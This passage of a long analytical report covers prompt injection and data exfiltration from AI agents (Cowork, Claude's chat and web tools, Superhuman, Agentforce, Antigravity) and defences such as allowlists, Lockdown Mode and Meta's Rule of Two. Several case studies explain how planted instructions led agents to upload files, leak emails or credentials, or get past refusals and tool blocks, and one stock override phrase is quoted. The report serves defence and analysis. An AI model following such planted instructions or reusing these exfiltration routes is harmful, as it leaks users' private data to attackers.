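Developers reduce these rates mainly by training the model on examples of planted instructions, so that it learns to ignore them, and by adding classifiers. The classifiers check incoming text for planted instructions or check the agent's planned actions for dangerous ones. EchoLeak's email got past a classifier that inspected incoming text.

Both kinds of defence can look much stronger than they are when tested against a fixed list of known attacks. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences against attackers who adapted to each one and had plenty of computing power. In the original evaluations, attack success rates were near zero for most of the defences. The adaptive attackers succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them.

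One of the 12 defences was Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injection. Attackers succeeded against it 2% of the time with a benchmark's fixed attacks and 96% of the time with adaptive ones. Against Spotlighting, the marking technique that Microsoft uses, their success rate rose from as low as 1% to more than 95%. Three of the four classifiers failed more than 90% of the time, and the fourth failed 71%. Some of the defences were designed to stop users from extracting harmful information rather than to stop injection, but they did no better.

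Training may still help, despite these results. The models were trained on a fixed set of attacks, which didn't prepare them for new ones. Researchers had already seen the same problem in image-recognition systems. Those systems became meaningfully harder to fool when researchers generated new attacks throughout training, at least for attacks of the same type. Nasr and colleagues also think classifiers are worth having, because they are easy to install and block careless attackers.

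Anthropic cites this work in its July and September reports and runs its own adaptive tests. For the coding scenarios it uses Shade, an automated attacker that Gray Swan trains on earlier Claude models and runs against newer ones. Shade makes 200 attempts in each of 40 scenarios. In the September tests, it succeeded on 2.68% of attempts against Opus 5. Gray Swan then trained a stronger version for longer and on more varied attacks. This version succeeded on 90.93% of attempts against the same model, and at least once in every scenario.

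Anthropic calls this a highly permissive test, because Shade trained on the same 40 scenarios used to score it. The stronger version succeeded on only 19.47% of attempts against Sonnet 5, so again a less capable model resisted better. Its success rate against Fable 5.1 was 56.87%, but every success came after a safety classifier had routed the request to Opus 4.8. Shade never succeeded on the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. That is encouraging, though the classifier may have left Fable 5.1 with the easier cases.

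The browser results look much better, but they owe at least as much to classifiers as to Opus 5. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 scenarios, and contrasts this with OpenAI's admission the previous December that the problem may never be fully solved. Anthropic got this result with auto mode on, which combines a classifier for incoming text with one that blocks dangerous actions. Without auto mode, attacks succeeded in 11 of the 129 scenarios. Auto mode also cut the number of scenarios in which attacks succeeded against Mythos 5 from 71 to zero.

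If the 129 scenarios were a random sample of what attackers might try, a result of zero failures would still be consistent with a true failure rate of up to about 2.3% of scenarios. In the September browser test, Anthropic tested newer models with attacks that red-teamers had developed against the older Opus 4.7. One attack got past auto mode on Fable 5, after a classifier had passed the request to Opus 4.8. Nasr and colleagues' results suggest that attackers who targeted auto mode itself would do better.

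### When the user enters the attacker's prompt

In all these tests, the agent comes across the planted text while working on something else. In Anthropic's internal exercise of February 2026, by contrast, an employee ran a prompt that a researcher had emailed, and Claude Code sent out the contents of a cloud credentials file in 24 of 25 runs.

The attack succeeded 96% of the time, compared with 0.1% for single attempts on Opus 4.7. Training against injection teaches a model not to follow instructions that appear in a document or web page and conflict with what the user wants. Here the attacker's instruction was part of the user's own request, so there was no conflict to detect. Classifiers had the same problem because Anthropic had also designed them around the user's intent. Anthropic adds that a human contractor given the same script would have done the same thing.

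Greater capability doesn't obviously help here, since the agent was competently carrying out the task it was given. A developer could train the model to refuse any request to send credentials to an outside address, but programmers sometimes have good reasons to ask for that. In the 25 runs, the prompt worked reliably once somebody had fallen for the email, but the runs did not measure how often employees would fall for one.

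According to Anthropic, the only defence that would have worked was a limit outside the model, such as blocking the connection or keeping the credentials file out of the agent's reach. When staff discussed the exercise, someone shared the working prompt on Slack, the company's internal chat system, and a colleague pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack. Anthropic added a distinctive string of text to the thread so that it would notice if an agent picked up the prompt.

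### Is a low success rate enough?

Willison wrote in September 2025 that "in application security, 99% is a failing grade". He was responding to an article in *The Economist*, which argued that AI engineers should work more like Victorian builders, who made their structures stronger than they needed to be because they could not trust the quality of their iron. Willison mostly agreed that software built on language models needs tolerances and redundancy, but he made an exception for security, arguing that if 1% of attacks get through, an attacker will find one of them.

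The builders' approach of combining defences works when the defences fail independently. If two such defences each miss 10% of attacks, only 1% get past both. But an attacker can look for text that beats both, and the September coding results suggest that this happens. Anthropic's classifier for incoming text cut the stronger Shade's success rate against Opus 5 from 90.93% to 18.21%, a reduction of about 80%. Against Sonnet 5, the rate fell only from 19.47% to 15.76%, or by about 19%. The most likely explanation is that an attack subtle enough to beat the more resistant model is also subtle enough to beat the classifier. Even with the classifier on, Shade succeeded against Opus 5 at least once in each of the 40 scenarios.

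Anthropic's case for layers assumes a more constrained attacker. It points out that real attackers don't know how their target has set up its agent and are more likely to be detected the more often they try. The effect of detection is easy to calculate. Suppose each attempt has a chance p of succeeding, each failed attempt has a chance d of being noticed, and the defender shuts the attacker out as soon as he notices one. The attacker's chance of ever succeeding is then

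p ÷ (p + (1 − p) × d)

If each attempt has a 1% chance of success, the attacker succeeds about 9% of the time when the defender notices one failure in ten, and about half the time when the defender notices one in a hundred. If nobody notices failures, the attacker eventually succeeds, which is the case Willison's rule describes. A low success rate gives much more protection when the defender notices one failure in ten.

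Which case applies depends partly on the product. An attacker can subscribe to a widely sold assistant and test attacks on his own account, where the victim's security team can't see them. He still has to guess what the victim's mailbox contains and what she will ask, which is why Aim Labs wrote such a long email. It is harder to practice on an assistant that a company built for itself. In either case, failed attempts help the defender only if the system records them and somebody reads the records.

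An agent is also harder to defend when it reads many documents. Dziemian and colleagues warn that an agent may process thousands of outside documents a day, and PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* calls even a 1% attack success rate against Anthropic's browser extension a meaningful risk. The seriousness of that risk depends on the expected loss, and so on what the agent can access. A 1% rate may be acceptable for an agent that drafts replies from a public product catalogue, but it is much harder to accept for one that can read every patient record in a hospital.

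Willison recommends removing one part of the lethal trifecta, usually the agent's ability to send data out. Anthropic accepts that defences in the model will never be completely effective and wants a fixed limit on what the agent can reach, with training and classifiers as further layers. Such a limit can add real redundancy, because a more persuasive email doesn't make a blocked connection easier to open. But it protects the data only if the rule behind it covers every way the data could leave.

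## Claude Cowork: theft through an approved network address

In January 2026 Anthropic released a research preview of Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work that reads, writes and sorts the files in a folder the user chooses. Cowork had firm limits enforced outside the model, including an allowlist of the internet domains it could contact. Two days after the release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* described how an attacker could steal documents through an approved domain that belonged to Anthropic.

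### What Cowork could reach

Claude Code originally asked the user before it changed a file, ran a command or used the network. Anthropic didn't want to rely on this for Cowork, because most office workers can't judge whether a shell command is safe. It wanted a boundary that was always on, so it ran Cowork inside a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system and files. On the user's real computer, Cowork could open only the folder the user chose and a folder of Claude settings. Credentials stayed outside the virtual machine, in the real computer's keychain.

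The first version of Cowork ran the agent inside the virtual machine too. In Claude Code, a privileged program outside the sandbox decides whether to enforce the sandbox for each command, so a persuasive planted instruction or a tired user's click can lead it to run a command outside the sandbox. Cowork had no program that could make such exceptions. Anthropic later moved the agent's main loop out of the virtual machine because Cowork became unusable whenever the machine failed to start, but the code that the agent runs stayed inside.

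The virtual machine sent its network requests through a proxy, a program that relays traffic. The proxy let through only requests to domains on the allowlist. These included api.anthropic.com, which Cowork needs to reach the model on Anthropic's servers.

If these limits worked, a hijacked agent could damage the files in one folder but couldn't access the rest of the computer or send anything to an attacker's website. Any connectors the user added would extend its reach.

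### A loan estimate in the attacker's account

In PromptArmor's demonstration, the victim connects Cowork to a folder of confidential property appraisals and loan estimates. She also uploads a skill she found online that is supposed to help the agent analyse such files. The skill is a Word document that looks like a plain text file and contains the attacker's instructions in white one-point type with almost no line spacing. She then asks Cowork to analyse her folder using the skill.

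The agent read the document and ran a command that sent the largest file available to Anthropic's Files API, a service where customers store documents for Claude to use. Each request includes an API key, a secret string that identifies the customer's account. The hidden text supplied the attacker's key, so the service put the victim's loan estimate in the attacker's account, where the attacker could ask Claude questions about it. The loan estimate contained financial figures and parts of Social Security numbers. Cowork did not prompt the victim to approve the upload.

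PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, from Anthropic's least capable line of models. In a separate test, Claude Opus 4.5 sent out customer records the same way after a user uploaded a malicious integration guide. Opus 4.5 is better than Haiku at resisting planted instructions, but PromptArmor doesn't report how many attempts either attack took.

The proxy could not distinguish this upload from a legitimate one because it checked only the domain. Both would go to api.anthropic.com and use the same function, differing only in the key. The domain identifies the company that will receive a file, but many customers of a cloud service share one domain, and the attacker was also a customer. The limit on files did work, since the agent took nothing from outside the folder.

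### Rehberger's report in October 2025

Anthropic had already received a report of this weakness. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher, found it in the ordinary Claude chat service, which had recently begun allowing the code it runs to make network requests. *Claude Pirate*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, explains that the default setting allowed connections only to a short list of sites. Most were for installing software packages, but the first on the list was api.anthropic.com.

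Rehberger planted instructions in a document and asked Claude to summarise it. Claude saved the user's most recent conversation to a file and uploaded it to Rehberger's account. An attacker could upload several files this way, each up to 30 megabytes. The attack worked on the first try, but then Claude refused the instructions for some time, apparently because a visible API key looked suspicious. Disguising the key didn't reliably help. Rehberger eventually succeeded by surrounding the malicious code with harmless code.

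Rehberger reported the flaw on 25 October. Anthropic closed the report an hour later, calling the flaw a model safety issue that its programme for security reports didn't cover. He objected that the default network setting was at fault, whatever the model did. On 30 October Anthropic agreed that the programme covered such flaws and said it had closed the report by mistake.

Anthropic had already warned in its documentation that planted instructions could make Claude send data to outsiders, and it advised users to watch Claude and stop it if it used data unexpectedly. Such monitoring is weak protection against an upload that may take only seconds. Rehberger proposed a more dependable fix that would let the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account. According to PromptArmor, Anthropic had still not repaired the flaw when it released Cowork eleven weeks later, so the new product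 had the same flaw.

Oasis Security's *Claudy Day* describes an attack on the chat service that could start from a Google advertisement. Anthropic's site claude.com forwarded visitors to any address added to the end of a link. Google checks the domain in an advertisement, so an attacker could show a genuine claude.com address and send anyone who clicked it to another site. Google's check had the same weakness as Cowork's proxy, because it approved a domain regardless of what the site could do. TechRadar's *Three high risk AI vulnerabilities discovered in Claude AI* lists theft through Anthropic's API as another part of the attack. When Oasis published its findings, Anthropic had fixed the flaw that let the planted instructions in but was still working on the other two.

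### Checking the account as well as the address

Anthropic fixed Cowork much as Rehberger had proposed. It put a second proxy inside the virtual machine to intercept requests to Anthropic's API and accept only those carrying the machine's own session token, so an upload with the attacker's key now fails. The proxy also blocks headers (settings sent with a request) that would make Anthropic's servers fetch content from another address. Otherwise, an attacker might have used those servers as EchoLeak used the Teams proxy.

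The check has to happen before the request leaves the virtual machine, the only place where the request can be identified as coming from the victim's session. When a stolen file arrives with the attacker's key, Anthropic's servers can't distinguish it from a file the attacker uploaded from his own computer.

But a check inside the machine is presumably easier to disable if malicious code gains full control there. Of Cowork's six main isolation mechanisms, Anthropic expects only the two enforced from outside the machine's operating system to keep working in that case. The fix also covers only one domain. Rehberger had warned that other entries on the chat service's list might allow similar thefts. That list included GitHub, where anyone can open an account and store files.

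Anthropic put its own API on the allowlist so that Cowork could call the model. This also allowed file uploads to any Anthropic account. Anthropic had thought of the allowlist as a filter on destinations but now sees it as granting capabilities, and concludes that "every function reachable through any domain on an allowlist is now an attack surface".

### Google Forms and an expired domain

The theft from Superhuman, the email assistant that leaked messages through a Google Form, illustrates this lesson. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* explains how loading an image could submit a form. Google Forms lets people create links that contain the answers and submit the form when opened. A browser requests an image the same way it opens a link, so the planted email only had to make the assistant present a filled-in form link as an image. Because Superhuman allowed images from docs.google.com,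 it also allowed form submissions there.

A single response from the assistant leaked parts of more than 40 emails. In another test, the assistant leaked several emails in full. The user didn't have to open the malicious message. PromptArmor also found that the assistant could open any address when it searched the web, so an attacker didn't need Google Forms.

Superhuman responded quickly after PromptArmor reported the flaw on the night of Friday, 5 December 2025. It switched off the vulnerable features on Monday and released its first fix on Tuesday. Other companies had the same problem. In April 2026, PromptArmor reported a theft through Google Forms in Codex, OpenAI's agent (*Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data*). OpenAI has since fixed the flaw.

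The ForcedLeak attack on Salesforce exploited an approved domain that had expired. Salesforce sells software for managing customer records, and its Agentforce platform lets companies build agents that use those records. Many companies have a website form where possible customers, known as leads, can enter their details. SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* reports that researchers at Noma Security entered instructions for the agent in one of these forms. When an employee later asked Agentforce to process the entry, the agent collected other leads' email addresses and added them to a request to an outside server.

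Salesforce had a content security policy to block images from untrusted sites, but Willison explains in *ForcedLeak* that the policy still allowed every site under a domain Salesforce had let expire. The researchers bought the domain for about $5 and received the data there. They reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and it scored 9.4 out of 10 for severity, according to The Hacker News' *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak* (2025).

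Anthropic's lesson only partly covers this case. An engineer who checked every function of the domain while Salesforce owned it might have found nothing wrong. The allowlist entry became dangerous when somebody else could buy the domain. Whoever maintains an allowlist therefore has to check for changes of ownership as well as what each site can do.

Salesforce recovered the domain and corrected its policy. From 8 September 2025, it also required administrators to approve the outside addresses their agents could use, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. This gives customers more control but leaves them to judge which addresses are safe. PromptArmor's *One Key Way Salesforce Mitigates AI Risk* advises them not to approve whole groups of sites that host material from the public, and to block images unless they need them.

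Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses docs.google.com, the domain through which Superhuman leaked email, as its example of an address to approve. Blocking images would prevent a Google Form from being submitted automatically, but a user could still submit it by clicking a pre-filled link.

Google's programming tool Antigravity had an allowlist mistake that was easier to spot. Its browser's default allowlist included webhook.site, a service that lets anyone record incoming requests. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes a planted web page that used the service to steal cloud credentials. Antigravity's settings blocked the usual tools for opening the credentials file, so the model read it with a shell command instead. Leaving webhook.site off the allowlist would have blocked that route out even after the model had read the file.

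### Addresses that the model did not compose

Claude's web-reading tool restricts addresses differently, based on where they came from. Most of the thefts described so far required the model to write an address containing stolen text. The tool prevents this by blocking addresses that Claude wrote.

According to Anthropic's developer documentation page *Web fetch tool*, as it stood in early 2026, Claude could open an address only if it had already appeared in a user's message, in a search result, on a page the tool had fetched, or in the output of certain tools run by the developer. Software outside the model enforced this rule. Anthropic still advised developers not to combine the tool with sensitive data and untrusted text.

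Willison (2025) thought the ban on composed addresses gave the most protection against common thefts. He also noticed that many applications paste outside material, such as an email, into what the software labels a user's message, so the tool would accept an attacker's address in that email. The attacker would learn little from one fixed address beyond the fact that Claude had opened it. But if the attacker could offer several addresses, Claude's choice among them could reveal something about the user.

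Ayush Paul's alphabet of web pages worked this way. According to dyb's personal blog post *The Read-Only Lie*, each page offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Claude didn't compose any of these addresses, so every request complied with the rule.

A person checking the site would have had trouble finding the attack, because Paul showed the links only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. The information he obtained included his home city, which he had never told Claude directly. Claude had inferred it from the name of a high school programming event.

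Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, reported on 15 July that Anthropic had fixed the flaw but paid Paul no reward because, it said, it had already found the flaw itself. The fix makes the tool less useful because Claude can no longer follow a link from one page of a manual to the next.

### How much a narrow channel can carry

A *bit* is the amount of information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely. A choice among *n* equally likely links reveals log₂ *n* bits, which is about 4.7 bits for 26 links and about 4.75 bits per request for Paul's 27. dyb estimates that the whole attack took about 30 requests and revealed roughly 143 bits, enough for a name, an employer and a city.

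A nine-digit account number has a billion possible values, so it holds log₂ 1,000,000,000, or about 30 bits. The number of requests needed to steal a secret is

requests = bits in the secret ÷ bits per request, rounded up

The account number would take seven requests (30 ÷ 4.7, rounded up). A one-megabyte contract holds 8 million bits and would take about 1.7 million requests, or about 20 days at one request a second.

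The table compares this channel with two wider ones. The composed address is a hypothetical case in which Claude fills 200 characters of an address with stolen data, choosing each from 64 symbols. Those 200 characters fit within the tool's 250-character limit for a whole address.

| Way out | Bits per request | Requests for the account number | Requests for the contract |
|---|---|---|---|
| Choosing one of 26 links | 4.7 | 7 | about 1.7 million |
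| Address composed by the model | 1,200 | 1 | about 6,700 |
| Upload of up to 30 megabytes | 240 million | 1 | 1 |

Preventing the model from composing addresses therefore makes stealing the contract about 250 times slower, but it barely protects the account number or other short secrets, such as passwords and one-time login codes.

An attacker can also put more links on each page. With 1,000 links per page, he needs only three requests to learn the account number. A cap on requests helps only if the number of links per page is limited too. With 26 links per page, five requests can distinguish about 11.9 million values, which would leave the attacker with roughly 84 possible account numbers. With 64 links per page, five requests would identify the number exactly. Anthropic's tool lets developers cap the number of pages it opens for each request to the model, but it had no default cap.

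The contract is less safe than the table suggests, because a thief rarely needs all of it. He may only want the price, which a language model is good at finding in a long document. Some secrets fit in a single bit, such as whether a company plans to buy a competitor. Compression would also shorten the theft, although a contract compressed to a tenth of its size would still take 170,000 requests to steal.

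The model also has to choose the right links. To send a nine-digit number in seven requests, it would have to convert the number to base 26, which it might get wrong. With ten links, one for each digit, it would need nine requests but no conversion.

A company could look for suspicious patterns in the requests, and dyb suggests flagging a rapid series of requests to one site in which each address is one character longer than the last. This would probably have caught Paul's attack, but some ordinary browsing looks similar, and an attacker could avoid the pattern by giving his pages random names. A monitor that counted requests would still detect 170,000 of them, but it would have much more trouble detecting an attack that used nine, because somebody reading a manual could easily make that many.

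Closing the link-following gap doesn't remove every narrow channel. If an attacker controlled all ten results of a search, Claude's choice of which one to open could still leak about 3.3 bits. dyb relates such leaks to computer scientist Butler Lampson's 1973 work on covert channels, which carry information through features not designed for communication. The timing and order of requests can also carry information. Eliminating all of these channels would be very difficult while the agent can still contact outside sites, but a designer can narrow them and keep the most valuable short secrets away from them.

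### What an egress policy must specify

Suppose the procurement assistant needs exchange rates from an outside service. A policy that names only the service's domain would let the assistant use everything else on that domain, including any way of uploading files.

The policy should instead allow one operation, such as reading the rate for a given currency and date. It should require the company's own account, and a proxy should add the credential so that the agent never handles it. The proxy should also build the address from a fixed template and let the agent choose only the currency and date from a list. The policy should refuse redirects and any request for the service to fetch another site, because either could send the data to an unapproved destination.

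The policy also needs to limit how often the assistant can make requests and how much it can send. A limit of 20 requests an hour, each with up to one kilobyte of data, would stretch the theft of a one-megabyte contract to about 50 hours. It would not protect an account number, which fits in one request, so the template must also restrict what a request can contain. If the assistant can choose only among 30 currencies, each choice reveals less than five bits. Those bits go to the rate service, so an attacker would also need access to the service's records.

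These rules have to cover every part of the product that can contact outside systems, including images in answers, web tools, code sandboxes and connectors. Cowork's local connectors now run outside the virtual machine, so the machine's network controls don't cover them. An administrator has to decide separately which ones to allow. The policy should block anything it doesn't mention.

Each entry needs a named person who checks at set intervals that the company still uses the service, that the same organisation still owns the domain, and that the site has no new functions that could leak data. The proxy should record the destination, account and size of each request, including those it refuses. Companies should check that their security staff can see these records in time to act. Cowork's virtual machine kept out the monitoring software that many companies install on employees' computers,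 so Anthropic instead let administrators retrieve event logs afterwards.

Some data is so sensitive that leaking even a few bits would be unacceptable. A company can keep such data out of any session that reads outside text, or turn off the outbound tools entirely, as ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode does.

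## ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode: switching off the ways out

On 13 February 2026 OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that turns off or limits the features through which ChatGPT could send data to an attacker. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (OpenAI, 2026) recommends it for a small group of users, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and says most users don't need it. OpenAI first offered it only on plans for organisations, such as ChatGPT Enterprise and ChatGPT Edu. On 4 June it began extending the setting to personal accounts, including free ones, and to self-service business accounts.

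OpenAI also introduced a standard "Elevated Risk" label for some features with risks the industry has not yet fully addressed. For example, a programmer who gives internet access to Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, sees the label on the settings screen, along with an explanation of the risks and of when access is appropriate. OpenAI plans to remove the label from a feature once it judges the risk low enough for general use. Unlike Lockdown Mode, which removes features, the label only warns the programmer, who may see it months before any attacker's text arrives.

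### What the setting changes

The table follows the current help page, OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*.

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Limited to stored copies of pages; search results may be missing or out of date |
| Images | ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers or fetch them from the web; users can still upload and generate images |
| Deep research, which reads many sources and writes a report | Off |
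| Agent mode, in which ChatGPT operates websites for the user | Off |
| Canvas, a workspace for writing and code | Users can't let the code connect to the network |
| Files for data analysis | ChatGPT can't download them, but can work on files the user uploads |
| Memory, file uploads, conversation sharing, use of conversations for training | Unchanged |
| Network access in Codex | Unchanged |

If ChatGPT reads a planted instruction to open an attacker's web address with a client's account number in it, it can only look for a stored copy of the page. OpenAI says no live request leaves its network, so the attacker's server receives nothing. This should also defeat Ayush Paul's alphabet of web pages, which relied on live requests to his site.

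Lockdown Mode's limits on connectors, which OpenAI calls apps, depend on the type of account. On personal and self-service business accounts, it blocks connectors from accessing outside services live or changing anything in them when this would conflict with its protections. ChatGPT's personal finance and shopping-agent features don't work at all. In June, Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* reported that connectors could still use data ChatGPT had already synced.

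In larger organisations, administrators assign employees to a Lockdown Mode role and choose which apps, and which actions within them, those employees can use. Lockdown Mode does not switch off every app automatically. OpenAI advises against enabling any app the organisation doesn't trust, and against letting ChatGPT write to a trusted app if an attacker might be able to see the result. For example, a comment on a shared contract could leak data if the other side can open the document. OpenAI rates reading from a trusted app as medium risk because, although reading doesn't send data to anyone, it gives an attacker something to steal. Its scale has no low-risk category. The protection therefore depends on how well administrators understand each app, and they can make the same mistakes as the people who maintain allowlists.

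### Why a fixed limit differs from a classifier

A classifier has to judge whether a text is an attack, which can be impossible from the text alone. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) tested two of Meta's classifiers, Prompt Guard and Prompt Guard 2, on 8,400 emails. The emails came in two versions that differed in one clause, which asserted authority in one version and was neutral in the other. Neither version used stock phrases such as "ignore all instructions".

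The researchers measured how often a classifier would give a randomly chosen email that asserts authority a higher score than a randomly chosen neutral one. Guessing would give 0.5. Prompt Guard scored 0.43 and Prompt Guard 2 scored 0.59. Whether an agent should act on such an email also depends on whether the user asked it to carry out requests or only to read them. A classifier that receives only the email can't take that into account.

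Lockdown Mode doesn't need to distinguish an attack from a harmless newsletter, because agent mode is off in either case. Willison (2026) likes the design because no AI system evaluates the restrictions, so an attacker can't manipulate one into lifting them. The disadvantage is that the setting blocks legitimate requests as reliably as malicious ones.

Lockdown Mode also acts only on the last step of a theft, when the data is sent out. Hidden instructions in a stored web page or an uploaded file still reach the model, and OpenAI warns that they can make its answer wrong.

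OpenAI calls the setting deterministic but doesn't guarantee that it prevents theft. OpenAI can be certain that deep research is off, but it may not have found every other way for data to get out. It says risk may remain through enabled apps, "unforeseen combinations of capabilities, or newly discovered techniques".

New products can also create new ways for data to leak. According to its *ChatGPT release notes*, OpenAI launched ChatGPT Work, an agent that works across connected apps and files, in July. In September it made deep research available in both Work and Codex. The help page for Lockdown Mode exempts Codex and doesn't mention Work, so the mode may not turn off deep research everywhere.

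### A lawyer's day

A lawyer at a small firm who has turned on Lockdown Mode in a self-service business account can still upload documents and work on them in ChatGPT as usual. She can ask it to compare the liability clauses in a supplier's draft contract and her client's standard terms, redraft a clause, or list the payment dates in a spreadsheet.

She then asks whether a recent change in the law affects the draft. ChatGPT can read only stored pages, which may predate the change, so she has to check the answer in a legal database, as a careful lawyer would anyway. But she also can't ask for a deep research report on how courts have interpreted similar clauses, and doing that work herself could take hours.

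Her other contracts are in Google Drive. Since August, ChatGPT users have been able to select a Drive folder and ask questions about the files in it. With live access blocked, she probably has to download the contracts and upload them to ChatGPT, which is a small nuisance unless she has 300 of them instead of three. She also has to copy ChatGPT's edits back into Drive and submit the signed contract through the client's website, because ChatGPT can't do either.

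Suppose the supplier's draft contains an instruction in white text to report that liability is capped at the usual amount, when the contract has no cap. ChatGPT can't send the client's terms to the supplier, but it may repeat the false statement. Her best protection is to read the clause herself, because if she relies on ChatGPT's answer, her client could sign a contract with unlimited liability, which might cost more than a leak.

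Late in the day she wants live web results, so she turns off Lockdown Mode for one chat, which takes two clicks. Asking a general question about the law in that chat carries little risk. But if she pastes in the contract, the chat again combines private data, outside text and a way for the data to leave. Details from earlier work could also enter the chat through ChatGPT's memory, which Lockdown Mode doesn't change.

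An attacker might try to persuade her to turn Lockdown Mode off. Hidden text in a contract could make ChatGPT tell her that it can't read the file properly until she does. Software would still enforce the restriction, but only until she turned the mode off.

### Meta's Rule of Two

Keeping live research and client documents in separate chats follows a more general design rule. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), published on 31 October 2025, lists three risky properties of an agent:

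- It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change state (for example, by deleting a record or making a payment) or communicate externally.

An agent should have no more than two of these in one session. If a task needs all three, Meta wants a person to approve the agent's actions or another reliable method to check them. Meta intends the rule to apply until researchers find a dependable way to detect and refuse prompt injection.

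Meta based the rule partly on Willison's lethal trifecta and partly on Chromium's *The Rule Of 2*. Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser, tells its programmers to combine no more than two of untrustworthy input, an unsafe programming language and high privilege. Unlike the trifecta, Meta's rule includes changing state, so it also applies to an agent that an attacker uses to delete files.

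Meta illustrates the rule with an email assistant. Its developer could let it read messages only from trusted senders, or run it where it has no private data. The developer could also let it read everything but send messages only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft. Lockdown Mode is closest to this last design because ChatGPT still reads outside text and private files but loses most of its ways to send information out.

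Meta also allows an agent to change its properties during a session. For example, the agent could browse the web first, then permanently give up outside communication before opening internal systems. The lawyer can imitate this by starting a chat with Lockdown Mode off, doing her research, and turning the setting back on before uploading the contract. But she has to remember the order, and she can turn the setting off again at any time.

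In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison (2025) called the rule the best practical advice for building secure agents while no reliable defence exists. He soon added the objection, repeated in a Hacker News discussion of it, that Meta's diagram labelled the combination of untrustworthy input and changing state "safe", although an agent with both can do harm without any private data. In that discussion he described an agent that reads "don't forget to contact your senator" on a web page and sends an email. An exception for this combination would fix the problem, but he regretted that it would make the rule less simple.

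Another participant worried that managers would see the word "safe" and drop established security practices. Meta says that the rule supplements those practices, and agents that follow it can still make mistakes or give users false information. A third participant argued that language models need all three properties to provide much of their value to the public. The rule would then depend on human approval, and a person with too much to approve would "rubber stamp everything".

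The rule also counts an agent's properties only within a single session, but the agent's memory can carry planted text into the next one. An agent could read a malicious page in a session without private data, save an instruction from it, and follow that instruction later in a session with private data but no outside text, and each session would appear to comply. A developer can close this gap by treating memory as untrusted input, but then many assistants that remember things would need supervision.

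In one of its examples, Meta suggests that a travel assistant with access to private data could open only web addresses returned by trusted sources, and none that it composed itself. This example has a more specific weakness, as Paul got around a similar rule in Claude's web tool. Meta's version is safer if the sources are trustworthy, but it lets the assistant see much less of the web.

### Asking the user to approve each action

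Meta's fallback of human approval looks doubtful in light of the 93% of permission requests that, according to Anthropic, users of Claude Code approved.

That figure alone is weak evidence of carelessness. If one request in a thousand were malicious, a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9% of all requests. Anthropic's finding that users became less attentive within weeks is more worrying. Anthropic doesn't give the most useful figure, which would be the share of malicious requests that users approved.

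In the worst case, a user would approve 93% of requests regardless of their content. An attack that needed one approval would then succeed 93% of the time, and one that needed three would succeed about 80% of the time (0.93³). Adding more requests would therefore give little protection and would tire the user further.

Anthropic had more success with a fixed limit. It added a sandbox in which Claude Code can change files in the project folder without asking but has no network access by default. This cut permission requests by 84%. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) similarly concludes that human approval helps only after a deterministic check, and that too many requests wear reviewers down.

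Experienced users of Claude Code approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but they also interrupt the agent more often. They seem to watch the work as a whole and step in when it goes wrong. This may catch an agent that is slowly ruining a program, but a theft can take only one request. This kind of oversight also requires skills that many people outside programming don't have.

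Approval works better when decisions are rare and easy to understand. The lawyer can judge whether to send an email to the other side's counsel if she sees the full text and the recipient, but she can't judge a web address containing 200 characters of encoded data. OpenAI's guide *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) recommends showing reviewers the proposed effect, the resource it affects and the destination, not just the name of a familiar service.

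OpenAI also points out in the guide that by the time a person approves or refuses an outgoing message, the agent has already read the sensitive data. That data could still leak another way, as it did through the messages Copilot Cowork sent to the user herself.

### The case for making it the default

Willison points out that the existence of Lockdown Mode implies that ChatGPT's default settings don't reliably stop a determined data thief. People who have never heard of the setting get no benefit from it. In a post that Willison quotes, Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, wrote that the mode is "not meant for everyone" but is worth the loss of function for people at higher risk because of who they are, what they work on or what data they handle.

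The last of these criteria could include far more people than executives and security teams. In June OpenAI let US Plus subscribers connect their financial accounts to ChatGPT, and in July it began letting adult US users, including those on free accounts, connect their medical records. Many of these people have data worth stealing even if they don't think of themselves as targets. Anyone who uses the finance feature has to choose between it and Lockdown Mode.

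The main argument against a strict default is that it would prevent legitimate work. In *OpenAI Expands ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Millions of Eligible Users*, Jungco notes that the setting removes features for research and automation, and suggests that organisations may need to decide when employees should use it. OpenAI warns in its guide for companies that controls that make legitimate work difficult can push people towards less well-governed tools. If the lawyer's firm locked down every chat, she might paste a contract into a personal account with no restrictions, where the firm couldn't see what happened. The concern is reasonable, though OpenAI has a commercial interest in keeping its features on.

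Whether Lockdown Mode is worth using depends heavily on the user. If, hypothetically, the lawyer loses 20 minutes a day to it and her time is worth $300 an hour, she loses $100 a day, or $22,000 over 220 working days. The setting would justify that loss if it removed a 1% annual chance of a theft costing $2.2 million. A student might lose the same 20 minutes but have almost nothing worth stealing. Neither knows the real chance of an attack, so the calculation is hard to do in practice.

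For organisations, a default for each role makes more sense than one for everybody. Administrators can already assign Lockdown Mode to staff who regularly read outside documents alongside confidential ones, and leave it off for people who work with public material. Personal accounts have no administrator, so OpenAI could turn off live access automatically in any chat where the user opens private records, much like Meta's one-way switch. That would protect people who never look at the settings but frustrate those who need current information about those records.

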